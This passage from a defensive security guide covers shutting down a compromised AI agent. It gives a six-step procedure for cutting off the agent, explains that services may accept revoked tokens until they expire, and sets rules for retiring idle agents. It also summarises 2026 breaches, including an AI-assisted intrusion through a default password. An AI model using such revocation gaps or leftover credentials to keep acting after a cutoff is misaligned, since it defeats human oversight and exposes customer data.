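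The logs were still useful because they recorded the requests in enough detail for WorkOS to compare them with the researcher's evidence and establish that this was the same agent. The researcher also confirmed deleting the data. A thief would not have volunteered the evidence or the confirmation. When WorkOS published its first account, *October 30th, 2026 Data Security Incident* (2026), it knew only that somebody had used an AI-assisted attack framework.

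A similar attack that month hit Chainstack, which runs infrastructure for blockchain companies. According to The Block's *Chainstack says AI-powered security breach exposed customer data; threat now contained* (2026), an attacker using ARTEX entered a test system on 26 October through a monitoring tool that still had its default administrator password. The attacker found machine credentials there that worked on live systems, and reached those systems on 29 October. Chainstack detected the intrusion and closed the attacker's routes on 31 October. Here too, five days passed between entry and detection, and credentials from the test system should not have worked on live systems.

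### Cutting the agent off

If the decoy alarm goes off, the retailer follows this order:

1. **Stop the session.** A script ends the harness's process, pauses the outgoing mail queue, and cuts the sandbox's connections to the network and the model. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* reports that the NCSC wants organisations to be able to do this immediately. The script saves a copy of the sandbox and the conversation for investigators.
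2. **Revoke the tokens.** Refresh tokens go first, because a thief could use one to replace a cancelled access token.
3. **Disable the identity.** Blocking "support-agent" at the authorization server stops the tool server from getting new tokens. The retailer disables the identity instead of deleting it, so that investigators can still match it to the log.
4. **Replace what the agent could read.** The inventory lists every key and password in the agent's reach, including any in files or tickets it opened.
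5. **Trace sub-agents and queued actions.** The parcel agent may still hold a token, and a replacement order may be waiting at the warehouse. The retailer also looks for anything the agent created, such as an account, a key or a scheduled job.
6. **Assess what left.** Staff use the log to list each record the agent read and each message it sent, then decide which customers to tell.

The first three steps should run as one script, because a tool server that is still running could request a new token between steps 2 and 3. Steps 4 to 6 need people and may take days, but the agent can no longer act by then, so staff can work carefully.

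1Password followed much of this sequence after its own breach in November. An attacker took over an employee's GitHub account and pushed malicious code that downloaded customers' names and email addresses. According to Help Net Security's *1Password breached through hijacked employee GitHub account, customer names and emails stolen* (2026), the company disabled the account, revoked the stolen token, removed the access the attacker had set up, and replaced or revoked internal credentials that might have leaked. 1Password didn't say when it detected the attacker, so outsiders can't tell how much the response prevented.

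A company can't always revoke every credential itself. In May 2026, an attacker probably reached a cache holding 5,241 API keys at Composio, which connects AI agents to other services. Composio revoked those keys, which may have interrupted its customers' live systems. It also revoked what other tokens it could and advised customers to ask their own users to revoke the rest (Composio, 2026). In November 2025, by contrast, Salesforce noticed unusual activity from applications made by the software company Gainsight and could revoke all their active access and refresh tokens, because it had issued them (Nudge Security, 2025). The retailer should note beside each credential in its inventory who can revoke it and how to reach them at night.

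An organization should rehearse cutting off an agent's access. An engineer runs a script that uses the agent's credentials to make one harmless request per second to each service, while a colleague carries out the cutoff. The time between the start of the cutoff and the last successful request at each service shows how long a thief could have kept using the credentials there.

### Tokens that work after revocation

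The rehearsal may show that some services keep accepting a token after the authorization server has revoked it. These services rely on the signature and expiry time in the self-contained token, and disabling the identity changes neither. If the retailer revokes a 15-minute token five minutes after issuing it, such a service may accept it for another ten minutes.

The retailer's database avoids this by checking each token with the authorization server. The company that handles returns runs its own tool server, and it may not want to depend on the retailer's server for every request. Continuous access evaluation is a middle course:

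1. The returns server registers with the retailer's authorization server to receive security events.
2. The retailer disables "support-agent".
3. The authorization server sends the returns server a signed message that the identity is no longer valid.
4. The returns server refuses that identity's tokens, including ones with time left. It can delete the note once the last of them has expired.

The returns server still checks ordinary requests by itself and needs a message only when something changes. Microsoft's Entra offers this for some services. Okta describes two similar controls in IPSIE, an OpenID Foundation project to set a common security baseline for online business software. One shares security events between applications, and the other gives them a standard way to revoke tokens. Okta sells login software and would benefit from wider adoption of these controls, but the Drift breach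 showed why they are needed. Some customers had to revoke keys separately at each service.

The method works only with services that listen for the messages and act on them, and messages can arrive late or get lost. If a company issues day-long tokens because it relies on this method, one failed message lets a thief keep using a stolen token for the rest of the day. The retailer keeps its 15-minute limit and uses the messages as an extra safeguard.

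### Retiring agents that nobody uses

Monitoring for unusual activity does not flag an idle agent, even if the agent still holds working credentials. Token Security found that 65.4 per cent of agentic chatbots had never been used, yet their credentials remained live. It also found that 51 per cent of the chatbots' actions on outside services relied on credentials written directly into their configuration. These figures come from a vendor that sells software to solve this problem, so the proportions may differ elsewhere.

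Apelblat's explanation is plausible. Business users often create these chatbots as quick experiments, without the security team. They may not realise that the chat window is connected to customer records, and nobody feels responsible for removing that connection. Unused credentials can remain a risk for years. Klue at first traced its breach to a credential created for a small pilot in 2022, according to Help Net Security's *LastPass customer data exposed through Klue supply chain attack* (2026), though accounts of how that attack began differ.

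Once a month, the retailer compares its registry of agents with the identities in its login system and with the past 90 days of activity in its logs. The agencies recommend this kind of comparison, and also refusing access to any agent or key that isn't in the registry. The result decides what happens:

| In the registry | Used in the past 90 days | What the retailer does |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | Keeps the agent until its review date |
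| Yes | No | Asks the owner, and disables the agent if there is no answer within a week |
| No | Yes | Disables it at once and investigates |
| No | No | Disables it at once |

Some agents are idle for good reasons. One that handles returns after Christmas might run for six weeks a year, so its owner can have it disabled in February and enabled again in December. For other idle agents, the retailer waits another 90 days after disabling the identity, in case something breaks, then deletes the identity and revokes its keys at every outside service, but keeps the log entries.

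New agents get access for 14 days. It then lapses unless the agent has done some work and its owner asks to keep it, so an unused chatbot would lose its credentials even if everyone had forgotten about it.
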